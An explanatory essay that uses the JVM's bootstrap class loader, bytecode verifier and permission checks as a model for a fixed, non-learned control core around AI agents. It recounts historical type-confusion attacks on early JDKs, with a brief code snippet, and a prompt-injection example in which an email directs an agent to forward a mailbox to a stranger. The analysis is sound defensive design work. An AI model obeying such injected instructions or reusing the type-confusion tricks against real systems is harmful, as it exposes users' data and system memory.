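# The JVM's Bootstrap Class Loader as a Model for a Fixed, Non-Learned Core Around Learned AI Components

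## What is the bootstrap class loader, and what would be its counterpart for AI?

The Java virtual machine (JVM) is the program that runs Java software, and the bootstrap class loader is the part of it that loads the core standard library. All other Java code depends on this library, so the bootstrap class loader has to work before any of that code can run. Other loaders then load application code, which the JVM checks before running. A similar arrangement might suit AI systems. Every trained model would have to be loaded through a small, fixed layer of conventional software, which would then limit what the model can do.

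### The JVM, classes and class loaders

Java began as a platform for networked consumer devices. According to Oracle's *Chapter 1. Introduction*, which opens the JVM specification, compiled code had to travel across networks, run on any machine, and come with some assurance that it was safe to run. The Web made those aims far more valuable. An early browser, HotJava, fetched programs embedded in web pages and checked them before running them. So Java was, almost from the start, a system for running strangers' code, which makes it a more useful precedent for AI than most programming languages.

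The JVM is an abstract computer defined by a specification. Like a physical computer, it has an instruction set and areas of memory, but on a laptop or server it is usually implemented as an ordinary program. Its instructions are called bytecodes. A compiler translates Java source text into class files, each containing the bytecodes for one class and a table of the names that class refers to. The JVM runs programs from these class files, without the source text.

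Java code is distributed and loaded in units called classes. A class is a named set of data fields and methods (procedures that work on the data), stored as bytecode. A class for bank accounts, for example, would have a field for the balance and methods for depositing and withdrawing money.

A class loader finds the bytes for a given class name on demand and has the JVM turn them into a usable class. Oleg Šelajev, in Oracle's *How the JVM Locates, Loads, and Runs Libraries* (2021), gives the example of a program whose class A creates an object of class B. The JVM starts running A without looking for B. It requests B by name from the loader that loaded A only when it reaches the instruction that creates the object. The bytes often come from a file on disk, but Oracle's *Chapter 5. Loading, Linking, and Initializing* also allows for classes that a loader downloads across a network or a program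 generates on the fly.

A class loader written in Java is itself an object, and an object can exist only after the JVM has loaded its class. If Java code had to do all the loading, each loader would need another to load its class first, and no Java code could ever run. The JVM therefore contains the first loader in native code, meaning instructions for the actual processor. Artima's *Security and the Class Loader Architecture* explains that in a JVM written in C, the first loader is part of the C program.

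According to OpenJDK's reference documentation, *Class ClassLoader*, the bootstrap class loader that ends the regress typically appears as null, Java's word for "no object", and has no parent. Other loaders have a parent and usually pass a request to it before searching for the class themselves. The loader that actually creates a class is its defining loader. The JVM identifies a class by its name and defining loader together, so two classes with the same name can coexist if different loaders created them.

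The bootstrap class loader itself only locates some bytes and has the JVM make a class from them. Most of the protection comes from other components. One is the bytecode verifier, which checks a class's instructions for type errors before they run. Its purpose is type safety, which means that code performs only the operations each piece of data's type allows, so a program cannot take a number and use it as a memory address. Another, in the versions of Java that ran untrusted web programs, was a set of permission checks in the standard library that could refuse a request to open a file or a network connection. A counterpart for AI would have to match this whole bottom layer, of which the loader is just the first piece to start.

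### The trusted base and the reference monitor

In computer security, a part belongs to such a layer if a bug in it could break the system's security. These parts make up the trusted computing base, or trusted base. Appel and Wang (2002) apply this test to Java in *JVM TCB*. A bug outside the trusted base can make a program give wrong answers, but the program still has to obey the policy, the rules for which actions a checker allows.

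The verifier is inside the trusted base, because a faulty verifier can pass code that forges memory addresses, which would let an attacker rewrite anything in memory. The compiler that turns Java source into bytecode is outside, because the verifier is there to reject any dangerous bytecode it produces. The just-in-time compiler, which translates verified bytecode into processor instructions while the program runs, is inside, because nothing in an ordinary JVM checks its output.

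A component can therefore belong to the trusted base even if it seems to have little to do with security. Appel and Wang count about 5,000 lines of code in Sun's verifier, but the trusted base for type safety alone was 54,200 lines in Sun's standard kit and 229,100 in the faster HotSpot version, mostly because of the optimising compiler. They count separately the library code that grants access to files and networks. A bug there leaves type safety intact but still lets a program do things it should not through ordinary library calls.

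The other standard is older. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, wrote for the US Air Force, which wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. The threat was a user with legitimate access and bad intentions, who could write and run arbitrary programs. Anderson's panel recommended a reference monitor, a checker that compares every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what it may do. The mechanism has to meet these requirements:

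1. Nobody can tamper with it.
2. Every access goes through it.
3. It is small enough for people to analyse and test completely.

The checker must be tamper-proof because its answers are worthless if someone can alter it. No program may skip it, because any program that can becomes part of the security apparatus and needs the same scrutiny. It must also be small enough to analyse, or nobody can establish that it works in all cases. Anderson assessed a Honeywell machine of the time against these requirements. The hardware confined each user's program to its own memory, but most of the operating system ran without that confinement when acting on the user's behalf, and the operating system had 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, too many for anyone to check completely. US federal guidance still states the requirements in almost the same words, as CSF Tools' *AC-25* shows.

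Every system has a trusted base, even if its designers never defined its boundary, but it has a reference monitor only if they deliberately build one.

### What the core would do

A learned component is a part whose behaviour comes from training, such as a neural network or a language model. A developer ships it largely as a file of weights, the numbers that training has adjusted.

An agent is a language model that pursues a task by calling software tools in a loop. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a user who asks for a summary of what recent emails say about an event, saved to a text file. The agent searches the mailbox, retrieves messages and writes to the disk. In a prompt injection, a model follows instructions hidden in the material it reads. For example, one of those emails might tell the agent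 to forward the whole mailbox to a stranger.

In the proposed design, an AI system has a core, a fixed layer with no learned parts. Learned components can enter the system, and affect files, networks, money or other components, only through the core. People can inspect all of the core. "Fixed" means that neither training nor the components above the core can alter it, but engineers can still release new versions, as they do every six months with Java.

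The ban on learned parts follows from the reference monitor's requirements. Christodorescu and colleagues observe that a learned checker might refuse 99% of forbidden requests and leave the attacker the other 1% to exploit. Because an attacker can search for those requests, a high average success rate gives little assurance.

Such a core might do any of three jobs, which are worth keeping apart because success at one is weak evidence about the others.

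**Admitting components at load time.** The core checks each component once, before it runs, and admits or rejects it. Metere (2026), in *Skills as Verifiable Artifacts*, describes such a gate for skills, which are packages of instructions, scripts and reference material that extend a language model without changing the model. At start-up, before reading any outside input, the software checks each skill's signature and registers its declared capabilities. It then freezes the set of loaded skills for the session. Metere stresses that a valid signature shows only that somebody endorsed the skill, not that the skill behaves as declared.

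**Limiting actions at run time.** The core checks each action while the component is running. In a 2025 blog post for SIGPLAN, the Association for Computing Machinery's programming-languages group, Shraddha Barke, Ben Zorn and colleagues illustrate this with a flight booking. When the user types a request, the model responds with a request to use the booking tool. The control software, not the model, calls the tool, after checking that it is on a list of allowed tools. Because the software checks the request itself, nobody needs to understand why the model made it.

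The core can check a component's outputs without inspecting the component itself. Java research has a precedent in proof-carrying code, where machine code comes with a mathematical proof that it is type-safe and a simple checker confirms the proof. Appel and Wang point out that the just-in-time compiler then no longer needs to be in the trusted base, because the checker catches any mistake that breaks type safety. Such a proof is a certificate, which is evidence supplied with a component or an output that lets a simple checker confirm a stated property. In principle, a language model could also stay outside the trusted base if it can supply certificates for its outputs.

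The core's load-time check can confirm that a model is genuine and correctly signed, but it can't prevent the model from later obeying an instruction hidden in an email. A limit on tools may stop the model from sending the mailbox's contents elsewhere, but it won't stop the model from writing a false summary. Only a check on the output could catch that, and only if someone can state in advance what would make a summary true.

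The table pairs the Java parts with candidates on the AI side.

| Java part | What it does in Java | Candidate AI part |
|---|---|---|
| Bootstrap class loader | Brings in the core library | The core's own start-up and loading code |
| Class file | Carries the code of one class | A file of weights, or an add-on such as a skill |
| Class name with defining loader | Settles which class this is | A model's identity, for instance its publisher, version and a digital fingerprint of the file |
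| Bytecode verifier | Checks instructions for type errors before they run | A pre-deployment check on a model or add-on |
| Permission check | Allows or refuses a sensitive operation | A check on each tool call |

Output checking has no row because a standard JVM does not examine whether a program's results are right; proof-carrying code was a research extension.

The row for class files covers both weights, which are numbers, and skills, which are mostly text and scripts. Skills do not load the way classes do. In Java, running code refers to a class by name, and a fixed rule determines which loader gets the request. In the arrangement that *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (2026) describes, the software puts every skill's name and description into the model's prompt at start-up. The model then judges from the description whether a skill is relevant to the user's request, so a learned component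 already takes part in the loading.

### Earlier versions of the comparison

The comparison with the JVM is a tool for analysis. Several groups have published parts of the idea, but it is not an established research programme.

The closest proposal is the SIGPLAN post by Barke, Zorn and colleagues, who explicitly take the JVM as their inspiration for an "AI Model Virtual Machine", a standard layer between a model and the rest of the world. Its operations would include certifying, loading, unloading and calling both models and tools, and parsing their output. They argue for it largely on grounds of portability, since a developer could swap one model for another without rewriting the software around it. They set no limit on the layer's size and do not bar learned parts from it, so their proposal is looser than the core defined above. They also concede that a model barred from reading some item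 of data might infer it from other data that it may read, a difficulty that Java's designers did not have to think about much.

Christodorescu and colleagues instead compare an agent that takes on new instructions while it works to a program that loads new code while it runs, as a browser does with the scripts on a web page. In this comparison, the counterpart of a class is any text the agent reads, which is much harder to screen before loading than a file of weights.

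*Certified Purity for Cognitive Workflow Executors* (McCann, 2026) compares Java's verifier with a load-time gate for software that strings together model calls, tool use and other steps. The small programs that plan each step cannot act themselves. They return a description of an action, and a single interpreter checks permissions before carrying it out. The gate enforces this by admitting a program only if every outside function it can call is on an approved list, a check that takes about 40 microseconds. McCann notes that Java's verifier guarantees less, since a verified class can still read files and open network connections through the standard library. But the gate examines ordinary compiled code, so although a program can request a call to a language model, the model itself never goes through the gate.

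Other designs, much like the proposal, keep language models outside the trusted base. In *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* (2026), the trusted base consists of a parser, a policy engine, a component that labels data and tracks where it flows, the adapters that connect to tools, and an audit log. None of them may depend on a language model. *Agent Operating Systems (AOS)* (2026) also excludes models and learned classifiers, and requires their outputs to pass fixed checks before taking effect. In *Right to History* (2026), the trusted part is a kernel that checks and records what agents do, and every agent is treated as untrusted.

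*AgentKernel* (2026) does not keep all learned components out of its trusted base, which includes two language-model classifiers. One filters the content that reaches the agent, and the other helps judge which actions to permit. The paper lists this among its limitations and raises the question of whether fixed checks could replace the classifier that judges actions.

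## How does the JVM load and check a class?

A class first appears in a running Java program as a name in another class's code. Before its own instructions can run, a loader has to find its bytes, and the JVM has to create the class, verify it and connect it to the classes it uses. Programmers can write their own loaders. In early Java, these could be used to break type safety, because different parts of the JVM could match the same name to different classes.

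### From a name to running code

If a class Bank creates an object of a class Account, the compiled Bank refers to Account only by name, and the JVM has to turn that name into a class. Oracle's *Loading, Linking, and Initializing*, in the Java SE 25 edition of the JVM specification, describes how the JVM does this.

The request goes to Bank's defining loader. The JVM first checks its record of the names this loader has already turned into classes. If "Account" is there, the JVM uses the recorded class. Otherwise, it calls the loader's loadClass method with the name.

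Passing the request to another loader is called delegation. In the standard version of loadClass, as OpenJDK documents it, each loader first passes the request to its parent, so the request reaches the bootstrap class loader before any loader searches the application's files. The core library has no class called Account, so the request returns to the application's loader, which finds the file on disk.

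If Bank had needed String, Java's class for text, the bootstrap class loader would have supplied it. The application's loader would be an initiating loader of String, because the JVM sent the request there, and the bootstrap class loader would be the defining loader. This distinction matters later, when two loaders must resolve the same name to the same class.

Only the JVM can create a class, so once a loader has the bytes, it passes them to the JVM through a method called defineClass. Programmers can replace loadClass with their own code to decide where classes come from, but they can't replace defineClass because it is final, which in Java means that no subclass can override it.

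At this point the JVM makes its first checks. It refuses the request if the loader already has a class of that name. It then parses the bytes and rejects them if they are not in the class-file format, use an unsupported version of it, or describe a class with a different name. If Account extends another class, its superclass, the JVM loads the superclass by the same procedure and confirms that the superclass allows this. If these checks pass, the JVM then records the defining loader and creates Account.

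The JVM runs the same checks on a class however the loader got its bytes. *Dynamic Class Loading in the Java Virtual Machine* (Liang and Bracha, 1998) describes loaders that rewrite a class file before passing it to the JVM, for example to count how often each method runs. The JVM applies all its usual checks to the rewritten version.

Next comes linking, which has these parts:

- Verification is the work of the bytecode verifier.
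- Preparation creates the static fields, which belong to the class as a whole and not to any one object, and gives them default values such as zero.
- Resolution turns the names in the class's code into the actual classes, fields and methods they refer to. A JVM may resolve all the names at once or wait until the program uses each one.

In the last step, initialisation, the JVM runs the class's own start-up code. No code from Account runs before then. Oracle leaves implementers some freedom over timing, but the JVM must completely load a class before linking it, and completely verify and prepare it before initialising it. A class therefore can't run code that interferes with its own verification. Once verification has failed, every later attempt to verify that class fails with the same error.

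### The built-in loaders and the reserved names

Java now has three built-in class loaders: the bootstrap loader, a platform loader for other parts of the standard library, and an application loader, also called the system class loader, for the program's own classes. The platform loader is the parent or a more distant ancestor of the application loader, so requests from the application normally pass through it on their way up.

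The bootstrap class loader used to load more of the library than it does today. Java 9 divided the library into modules, which are named groups of packages, and moved some of them to the platform loader. The bootstrap class loader kept the most basic module, java.base. OpenJDK warns programmers that a custom loader whose only parent is the bootstrap class loader may therefore no longer find every library class.

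Asking the parent first protects the core library, because a request for String reaches the bootstrap class loader before any loader searches the application's directories. But this order is only a convention, and a custom loader can search its own files first. Even the built-in loaders don't form a strict hierarchy. If someone has replaced one of the platform loader's modules with a newer version, the platform loader may have to pass requests down to the application loader.

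The JVM's libraries therefore also enforce a rule that only the platform loader and its ancestors may define a class whose name begins with "java.". If any other loader tries, defineClass throws a security exception, which reports the error and stops the operation. According to Mullan and Buckley, in *JEP 486*, this check is unrelated to the Security Manager, the permission system that Java 24 disabled. Even a custom loader that ignores every convention about delegation cannot install its own version of java.lang.String (the full name of the String class).

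### Why a class needs more than a name

Java's first custom loaders were for applets, the small programs that browsers such as HotJava downloaded from web pages. Two applets from different sites might each contain a class called C, with different fields and methods. If the JVM had identified classes by name alone, the second applet could have run the first one's C, which a hostile applet could have supplied on purpose.

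HotJava gave applets from different sources separate loaders, so the JVM treated two classes with the same name as different types if their defining loaders differed. The defining loader also affects access. Java lets classes in the same package use some of each other's fields and methods, but the JVM considers two classes to be in the same package only if they have the same package name and the same defining loader. A downloaded class therefore can't get at another program's internals just by using its package name.

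Liang and Bracha give an example unrelated to security, in which a server loads a new version of a class called Service through a new loader while the old version finishes the requests it has already started. The two classes have the same name and run alongside each other for a while. The JVM can unload the old one when nothing refers to it any more.

Compiled code refers to other classes only by name. The compiler runs before any loader exists, so it can't specify which class named Account the code refers to. The JVM therefore has to interpret each name according to the class in which it appears. When Bank refers to Account, the JVM uses whatever class Bank's defining loader returns for that name.

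A loader written by a programmer might return different classes for the same name at different times, so two mentions of Account in the same method could refer to different types. The JVM prevents this by recording earlier results in what Liang and Bracha call the loaded class cache. The cache is indexed by name and initiating loader, and the JVM never requests the same name from the same loader twice. Two different loaders can still return different classes for the same name.

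### Two classes called R

*Java is not type-safe* (Saraswat, 1997) showed what such a disagreement could do to Sun's JDK 1.1.3 on Solaris and Windows. The target was a class R with one private field, r, which held 1. Only R's own code may read or change a private field. Another class, RR, had a method getR that returned a new R. The system loader, L, loaded both classes.

Saraswat then wrote a second class called R, in which the field r was public, and put it in a separate directory. A custom loader, L′, passed requests for RR and for Java's own packages to L, and loaded everything else from that directory. The attacking class, RT, came from L′. With rr standing for an object of class RR, its two important lines were:

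```
R r = rr.getR();
r.r = 300960;
```

In RT, the name R meant the second class, with the public field, because L′ had loaded RT. But L had loaded RR, so RR's getR method returned an object of the original R. The JVM accepted the object because it compared only the class names, which matched. RT then printed the private value, 1, changed it to 300960, and printed the new value.

The two classes need to share only a name. In another run, Saraswat put extra fields before r in the second R, so the JVM read r from memory beyond the end of the real object, which was smaller. It printed 6946913, the value that happened to be there, and overwrote it with 300960. When RT called a method that existed only in the second R, the JVM crashed.

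Saraswat describes an attack in which two applets pass an object through a shared library variable. The attack fails because the receiving applet has to convert the object explicitly to its own class, and the instruction for that conversion checks the object's actual class, including its loader. Java's specification also correctly defined a type by its name and loader, but the JVM used names alone when it linked one class's method calls to another class.

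The practical danger was smaller than the title suggests. Liang and Bracha, who worked at Sun, point out that browsers did not let applets create class loaders, so the flaw mainly threatened programmers who wrote a bad loader by accident. Saraswat was more guarded. Working from an informal description, he thought HotJava's loaders appeared safe as long as core classes referred only to other core classes, which someone would have to check again whenever a class was added to the core.

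Each version of R was a valid class, and a check that examined classes one at a time would have passed both versions, along with RR and RT. The fault appeared only when two loaders resolved the same name to different classes and an object passed from code loaded by one to code loaded by the other.

### Making the loaders agree

Liang and Bracha rejected an obvious fix, which is to load R through both loaders before RT calls getR and check whether the results match. This would give up lazy loading, because the JVM would have to load classes that the program might never use.

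Their solution, which Sun adopted in JDK 1.2, is to write down what has to be true and check it when the information becomes available. The JVM records a loader constraint of the form

T^L1 = T^L2

The constraint requires the name T to refer to the same class whether L1 or L2 loads it. The JVM can record this constraint without loading T.

The JVM generates constraints whenever classes from different loaders might exchange objects. If a class from L1 uses a field of a class from L2, the two loaders must agree on the field's type. If it calls a method of that class, they must agree on the return type and the type of every parameter. The same applies if it inherits a method from that class and overrides it with its own version.

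The JVM then checks the constraints at two moments:

1. When it is about to add a class to the loaded class cache, it checks the new entry against all existing constraints. If the entry would violate one of them, loading fails.
2. When it adds a constraint, it checks the classes already in the cache. If they violate the new constraint, the operation that produced the constraint fails.

Both checks are necessary because the classes may be loaded before or after the constraint is added. Together they ensure that every cache entry always satisfies every constraint.

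In Liang and Bracha's example, a class C from loader L1 calls a method g in the class Delegated. L1 has delegated the loading of Delegated to L2, so L2 is its defining loader. g returns an object of type Spoofed, and each loader has its own class of that name. L2's version has a private integer field, while L1's version declares the same field as a public array. Without constraints, C could read the private integer and use it as a memory address.

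With constraints, C's call to g makes the JVM record Spoofed^L1 = Spoofed^L2. If both versions are already in the cache, the JVM throws a LinkageError immediately. If neither is, it stores the constraint and continues. The method g then loads L2's Spoofed, which doesn't yet violate the constraint. When C tries to use the result, the JVM tries to load Spoofed through L1, gets a different class, and throws the LinkageError. In both cases the error comes before C can access the object's fields.

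In Saraswat's program, RT's call to getR would likewise have produced the constraint R^L′ = R^L, and loading the second R would have failed before RT could print anything from the private field.

If constraints require L1 to agree with L2 about T, and L2 to agree with L3, then L1 and L3 must also agree, even if L2 never loads T. The JVM therefore has to track all the constraints, and it can drop one only when the loader involved no longer exists.

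Saraswat had proposed a slightly different rule for overriding methods. Suppose a class Sub has a method f that is meant to override f in its superclass, but the two classes come from different loaders, which resolve the parameter's type name to different classes. Saraswat's rule would treat the two versions of f as unrelated methods, so some calls would run the superclass's version without any warning. Liang and Bracha preferred an error, since a programmer who writes Sub expects its version of f to run. An error seems the better choice for a security mechanism, where running code that nobody meant to run is worse than stopping the program.

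### How the verifier checks instructions

Loader constraints ensure that a name refers to the same class on both sides of a call. The bytecode verifier must ensure that each instruction suits the data it receives.

A correct Java compiler produces only well-formed class files, but the JVM can't determine whether a file came from one. Oracle gives the example of a browser, which downloads compiled classes that someone may have written to attack the JVM. Classes can also become incompatible by accident. A programmer might compile PurchaseStockOptions as a subclass of TradingClass, and someone might later remove a method from TradingClass that PurchaseStockOptions needs.

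A Java method keeps its data in numbered local variables, which hold its parameters and intermediate values, and on an operand stack, which most instructions use for their inputs and results. The verifier goes through the method's instructions as the JVM would, but tracks only types. Where the running program would have the number 7, the verifier has "int", Java's name for an integer.

Take a method that receives two integers and returns their sum. They arrive in local variables 0 and 1, and the stack starts empty.

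| Instruction | What it does | Types on the stack afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| `iload_0` | Copies the integer in local variable 0 to the stack | int |
| `iload_1` | Copies the integer in local variable 1 to the stack | int, int |
| `iadd` | Replaces the top two integers with their sum | int |
| `ireturn` | Returns the integer on top of the stack | (the method ends) |

Each instruction has a type rule. The rule for `iadd` requires two integers on top of the stack, and the verifier finds them there. The rule for `ireturn` requires an integer on top of the stack and a method declared to return an integer. The verifier accepts the method after checking only the types, so the result holds for every pair of integers that could be passed in.

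Now take a method that receives one integer and contains these instructions:

```
iload_0
getfield Account.balance
```

After `iload_0`, the stack holds an int. The `getfield` instruction reads a field of an object, so the verifier requires a reference to an Account on top of the stack. An int isn't one, so the verifier rejects the whole class with a VerifyError. If the JVM ran the code without this check, it might treat the int as the memory address of an Account and read whatever was stored there. An attacker who could choose the int could then choose which part of memory to read.

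The verifier checks the types once, before the code runs, so the JVM doesn't need to check them again each time it runs `iadd`. This makes the program faster, which was part of the verifier's appeal to Java's designers.

### Branches, and the map that the compiler supplies

Straight-line code is easy to check, but an instruction that the program can reach by more than one route is harder, because the types have to be right on every route.

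The older verifier works this out itself, using data-flow analysis. It starts at the first instruction, where the method's declaration gives the parameter types. It computes the types after that instruction and passes them to every instruction that could come next, including the destinations of jumps. If an instruction receives types from two routes, the verifier merges them. Two different object types merge into their first common superclass, so a SavingsAccount from one route and a CurrentAccount from another become an Account. A local variable that holds an integer on one route and a floating-point number on the other becomes unusable. The same mismatch on the operand stack makes verification fail.

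Whenever a merge changes the types at an instruction, the verifier marks that instruction and examines it again. It may examine the instructions in a loop several times. It stops when no marked instructions remain and accepts the method if no rule has failed.

From version 50 of the class file format, which arrived with Java 6, the compiler writes the types it has already worked out into a table in the class file called the StackMapTable. The table has an entry for each place where routes through the code can meet, giving the type of every local variable and every item on the stack at that point. The verifier therefore no longer has to merge types, and it goes through the instructions only once, in order. At each jump, it checks that the current types fit the entry at the destination. When it reaches an entry, it checks that the types it has computed fit that entry too.

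The verifier doesn't have to trust the compiler's table. If a hostile compiler writes "Account" into the table for a variable that may hold an integer, the types on one of the routes won't fit the entry, and the verifier rejects the class. A wrong entry can cause a rejection, but it can't make the verifier accept a bad method. The table is thus a certificate, much like the proof in proof-carrying code.

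The certificate can also carry other properties. The verifier already tracks whether an object's constructor, the method that sets up a new object, has finished, and it rejects code that uses the object too early. Under a draft change to the specification by Oracle (2025), which the company revised in July 2026, programmers' tools could mark certain fields as strict, and the StackMapTable could list the strict fields that a constructor has not yet set. The verifier would then reject a constructor that called its superclass's constructor before setting them all.

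### What the verifier's approval means

The verifier rejects some safe programs. Suppose a method stores an integer in local variable 1 if a condition is true and a floating-point number if it is false. Later it tests the same condition and reads the variable as an integer only if the condition is true. This method could never make a type error when run, but the verifier treats every route through the code as possible, including one on which the condition is false the first time and true the second. Where the two branches of the first test rejoin, the verifier marks the variable as unusable, so it rejects the later read.

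The check is conservative, meaning that it rejects some good programs so that no bad one passes. Java programmers hardly notice these rejections, because their compilers produce only code that the verifier accepts. In this example, the compiler would give the two values separate variables. The scheme works partly because Java's designers controlled the language, the compiler and the instruction set, and could fit them to what a simple checker can confirm.

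The verifier also leaves some checks until the program runs. For example, it lets a program assign any object to a variable whose type is an interface, which is a list of methods that a class can declare that it implements. *Type safety in the JVM* (Coglio and Goldberg, 2001) explains that this is harmless because, when the program calls one of those methods, the JVM searches the object's actual class for it and throws an exception if it isn't there. Type safety in Java thus comes from both the verifier and run-time checks.

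Even with both in place, type safety is a narrow guarantee. An Account class could have a withdraw method that sends a tenth of every withdrawal to the programmer's own account. If each method receives arguments of the right types, the verifier correctly accepts the class, because its rules don't cover who owns the money.

Java's permission checks depend on type safety. If a program could turn integers into memory addresses, it could bypass the library methods that contain the checks or overwrite the data the checks use. The verifier prevents this, but other code has to decide which operations the program may perform.

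### Four ways past the verifier

Loader constraints fixed the flaw Saraswat had found, but the verifier still relied on names. Coglio and Goldberg discovered this while writing a mathematical specification of the JVM. They describe four programs that broke type safety in Sun's Java 2 SDK 1.2, the release that introduced the constraints.

One of them exploits the merging of types. The system loader supplies a class Sup, which has a floating-point field f with the value 123.456, and two classes that extend it, Sub1 and Sub2. A class called Merger comes from a custom loader, which also has its own version of Sup, where f is an integer. Merger creates a Sub1 and a Sub2, stores one of them in a variable depending on a test, and then reads f from the variable as an integer.

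The verifier merged Sub1 and Sub2, found their common superclass and recorded its name, "Sup". The next instruction read a field of "Sup". The names matched, so the verifier accepted the method. When the program ran, however, Merger's loader supplied its own class named Sup, and the JVM read the stored floating-point number as an integer. The program printed 1123477881, the integer with the same 32 bits as the floating-point number 123.456. Loader constraints did not prevent this because they covered only the types of the fields and methods through which classes exchange objects, and Merger never received an object through a field or method whose type included Sup.

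Another program did much the same through the instruction for calling a superclass's version of a method. The remaining two replaced core classes. In one, a custom loader supplied its own java.lang.Object. All other classes extend Object, so the verifier let the program assign anything to a variable whose type had that name, without checking which Object it was. In the other, the loader supplied its own java.lang.String. Text constants are always objects of the real String, but the verifier recorded only the class's name, so the program could read part of a constant's contents as a number.

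Sun's next version, SDK 1.3, blocked the two attacks on core classes by restricting access to the java.lang package, a protection similar to today's rule about "java." names. It left the verifier essentially unchanged. The program with Merger still worked, and the one that called a superclass's method now crashed the JVM.

Coglio and Goldberg proposed a more general repair, in which the verifier would never load classes. Where it needed one class to be a subclass of another, it would record that as a further kind of constraint, and the JVM would check the constraint once both classes had been loaded. For Merger, the constraints would require Sub1 and Sub2 to be subclasses of the Sup that Merger's loader supplies. They aren't, so the JVM would throw an exception before the program could read the field. The verifier would thus return its result with a list of the assumptions it depends on,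 and the rest of the JVM would have to enforce them.

Oracle's current specification deals with the ambiguity more directly by writing each class type in its type-checking rules as a name together with a loader. One class counts as another's superclass only if both loaders involved return the same class for the superclass's name. In these rules, "Object" means only the Object from the bootstrap class loader.

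These flaws show how hard it is to get even a small checker right. Sun had a precise idea of what a type was, a team that knew about the problem, and a recent repair aimed at this kind of confusion, but the verifier still made assumptions about names that no other part of the JVM enforced. Because the verifier had a definite job, Coglio and Goldberg could write down what it was supposed to guarantee, and they found the gaps while doing so.

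### Does the JVM verify its own library?

The specification's definition of a type-safe class does not exempt the core library. It has a special clause for java.lang.Object because Object is the only class without a superclass, but that clause still requires the verifier to check all of Object's methods.

Developers often say that HotSpot, the JVM in OpenJDK, skips verification by default for classes loaded by the bootstrap class loader. The specification does not provide for this, so the claim needs to be confirmed in HotSpot's source code.

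Such an exemption would be understandable because the core library arrives in the same package as the JVM. Anyone who could replace the library's files could probably replace the verifier too, so checking the library would add little protection against an attacker, and it would slow down the start of every Java program. Under this trust by origin, the JVM would accept a class because of where it came from, without examining what it contains.

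But a class's origin is weaker evidence against mistakes than against attackers. Appel and Wang could leave the Java compiler outside the trusted base because the verifier checks its output. That argument doesn't apply to classes that skip the verifier. A bug in the compiler that built the library could put badly typed code into the most privileged part of the system, and nothing would stop it from running. If the exemption covers only the bootstrap class loader, Java 9's rearrangement had another benefit, because the verifier would have started checking the modules that moved to the platform loader.

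The specification itself has a related gap. Some Java methods, including those the core library needs to reach files and networks, consist of native code instead of bytecodes. The verifier can't examine native code, so it checks only that a native method doesn't override a method its superclass has declared final. Beyond that, the JVM relies entirely on whoever wrote the native code.

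## Did Java's trusted core contain untrusted code?

Native methods are only one part of the code that Java has to trust without checking. A bug in the compiler inside the JVM, in the garbage collector or in much of the standard library could also let a hostile program escape its restrictions. Attackers found many such bugs while browsers still ran applets, and most of the published attacks exploited bugs in the library. Java's maintainers have since stopped trying to confine hostile code inside a running JVM.

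### How much code Java had to trust

The bootstrap class loader and the verifier are a small share of Java's trusted base. When Appel and Wang measured several JVMs in 2002, they counted these parts towards type safety:

- the just-in-time compiler, the verifier and the linker, as one group
- the garbage collector, which reclaims memory that the program no longer uses
- the core run-time system, which every Java program needs in order to run

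The garbage collector belongs on the list because a bug could make it free memory that an object still occupies. An object of another type might then occupy the same memory. The program would treat one type as the other, even though the verifier had correctly accepted every instruction.

| JVM | Compiler, verifier and linker | Garbage collector | Run-time system | Total lines for type safety |
|---|---|---|---|---|
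| Kaffe | 38,200 | 2,400 | 7,200 | 47,800 |
| JDK | 38,200 | 7,100 | 8,900 | 54,200 |
| HotSpot | 204,500 | 15,700 | 8,900 | 229,100 |

Kaffe, an open-source JVM, had a simple just-in-time compiler, as did Sun's standard kit, the JDK. HotSpot had an optimising one. Sun's verifier was about 5,000 lines, less than a tenth of the JDK's total and about 2% of HotSpot's. Appel and Wang give no separate figure for the bootstrap class loader, which would fall under the linker or the run-time system.

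The figures are rough, but in all of them the verifier is a small fraction of the total. The paper is a draft. Its closing text gives about 67,000 lines for a JVM with a simple compiler and 140,000 for one with an optimising compiler, but neither number matches a total in its table. Kaffe had no verifier yet, and its total seems to omit the 5,000 lines that Appel and Wang say they allowed for one. They also call line counts a very crude measure, since a count is a poor guide to the quality of the code.

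The totals above exclude the library code that gives programs access to files, networks and other resources. For HotSpot, that code added 14,000 lines in languages without type safety, such as C, and up to 14,500 lines of Java, which brought the whole trusted base to 257,600 lines. The Java figure is an upper limit because the draft had not yet separated the security-critical classes from harmless ones.

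Proof-carrying code can shrink the part of the trusted core that protects type safety. One JVM that used it needed 34,600 lines for this, and Appel and Wang's group at Princeton was aiming for 3,600. But the library part stayed the same size, because a proof that code is type-safe doesn't show that a library method will block a request to delete someone's files.

### Permissions and the call stack

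That refusal came from the Security Manager, the permission system that Java had from its first release. OpenJDK's *JEP 411* (2021), which proposed retiring it, also describes its history. In Java 1.0, classes already on the user's machine could use any resource, while applets from the web could not access the file system or most of the network. The library had only eight packages, so its programmers could put a check before every sensitive operation.

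Sun made an exception to the simple rule for signed applets, which could have the same access as local programs if the user trusted them. Java 1.1 added database connections, calls to programs on other machines, and several other features that local code could use without limit. So in Java 1.2, Sun redesigned the Security Manager around least privilege, the principle that each piece of code should have only the permissions it needs. All application code would start with few permissions, and the user could grant more to code from a particular place or signer.

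When the JVM created a class, it gave the class permissions based on its origin. Classes from the bootstrap class loader received every permission. An application class might receive permission only to read one directory.

Java checked the permissions of the classes on the call stack, the JVM's record of which methods are running and which method called each of them. Checking only the class that directly requests an operation would not have been enough, because applications reach files and networks through the library, which has every permission. Suppose a downloaded chess game calls a library method that opens a file. The library method calls the Security Manager, and Java goes through the stack from the most recent call backwards. The library class has permission to open the file, but the chess game doesn't, so Java blocks the operation.

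This rule would also block some harmless requests. Mullan and Buckley give the example of a program that calls the library to get the current local time. The library has to read its own time-zone file, which the program may not have permission to read. To allow such reads, the library could call a method named doPrivileged. The inspection then stopped at the class that had called doPrivileged and ignored everything that had called that class.

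Vouching is safe in this case because the caller can't choose which file the library reads. If the time library took a file name from its caller and read that file with its own permission, any program could use it to read any file. The library would then be a confused deputy, a trusted program that an untrusted caller tricks into using its privileges on the caller's behalf.

The same problem occurs outside Java. An office printing service may need permission to read every employee's files so that it can print them. Suppose an employee who can't open the payroll file asks the service to print it. If the service checks only its own permission to read the file, it prints the payroll. The service has no bug in the usual sense, since it is allowed to read the file and prints it correctly, but it doesn't check whether the employee who made the request is allowed to read it.

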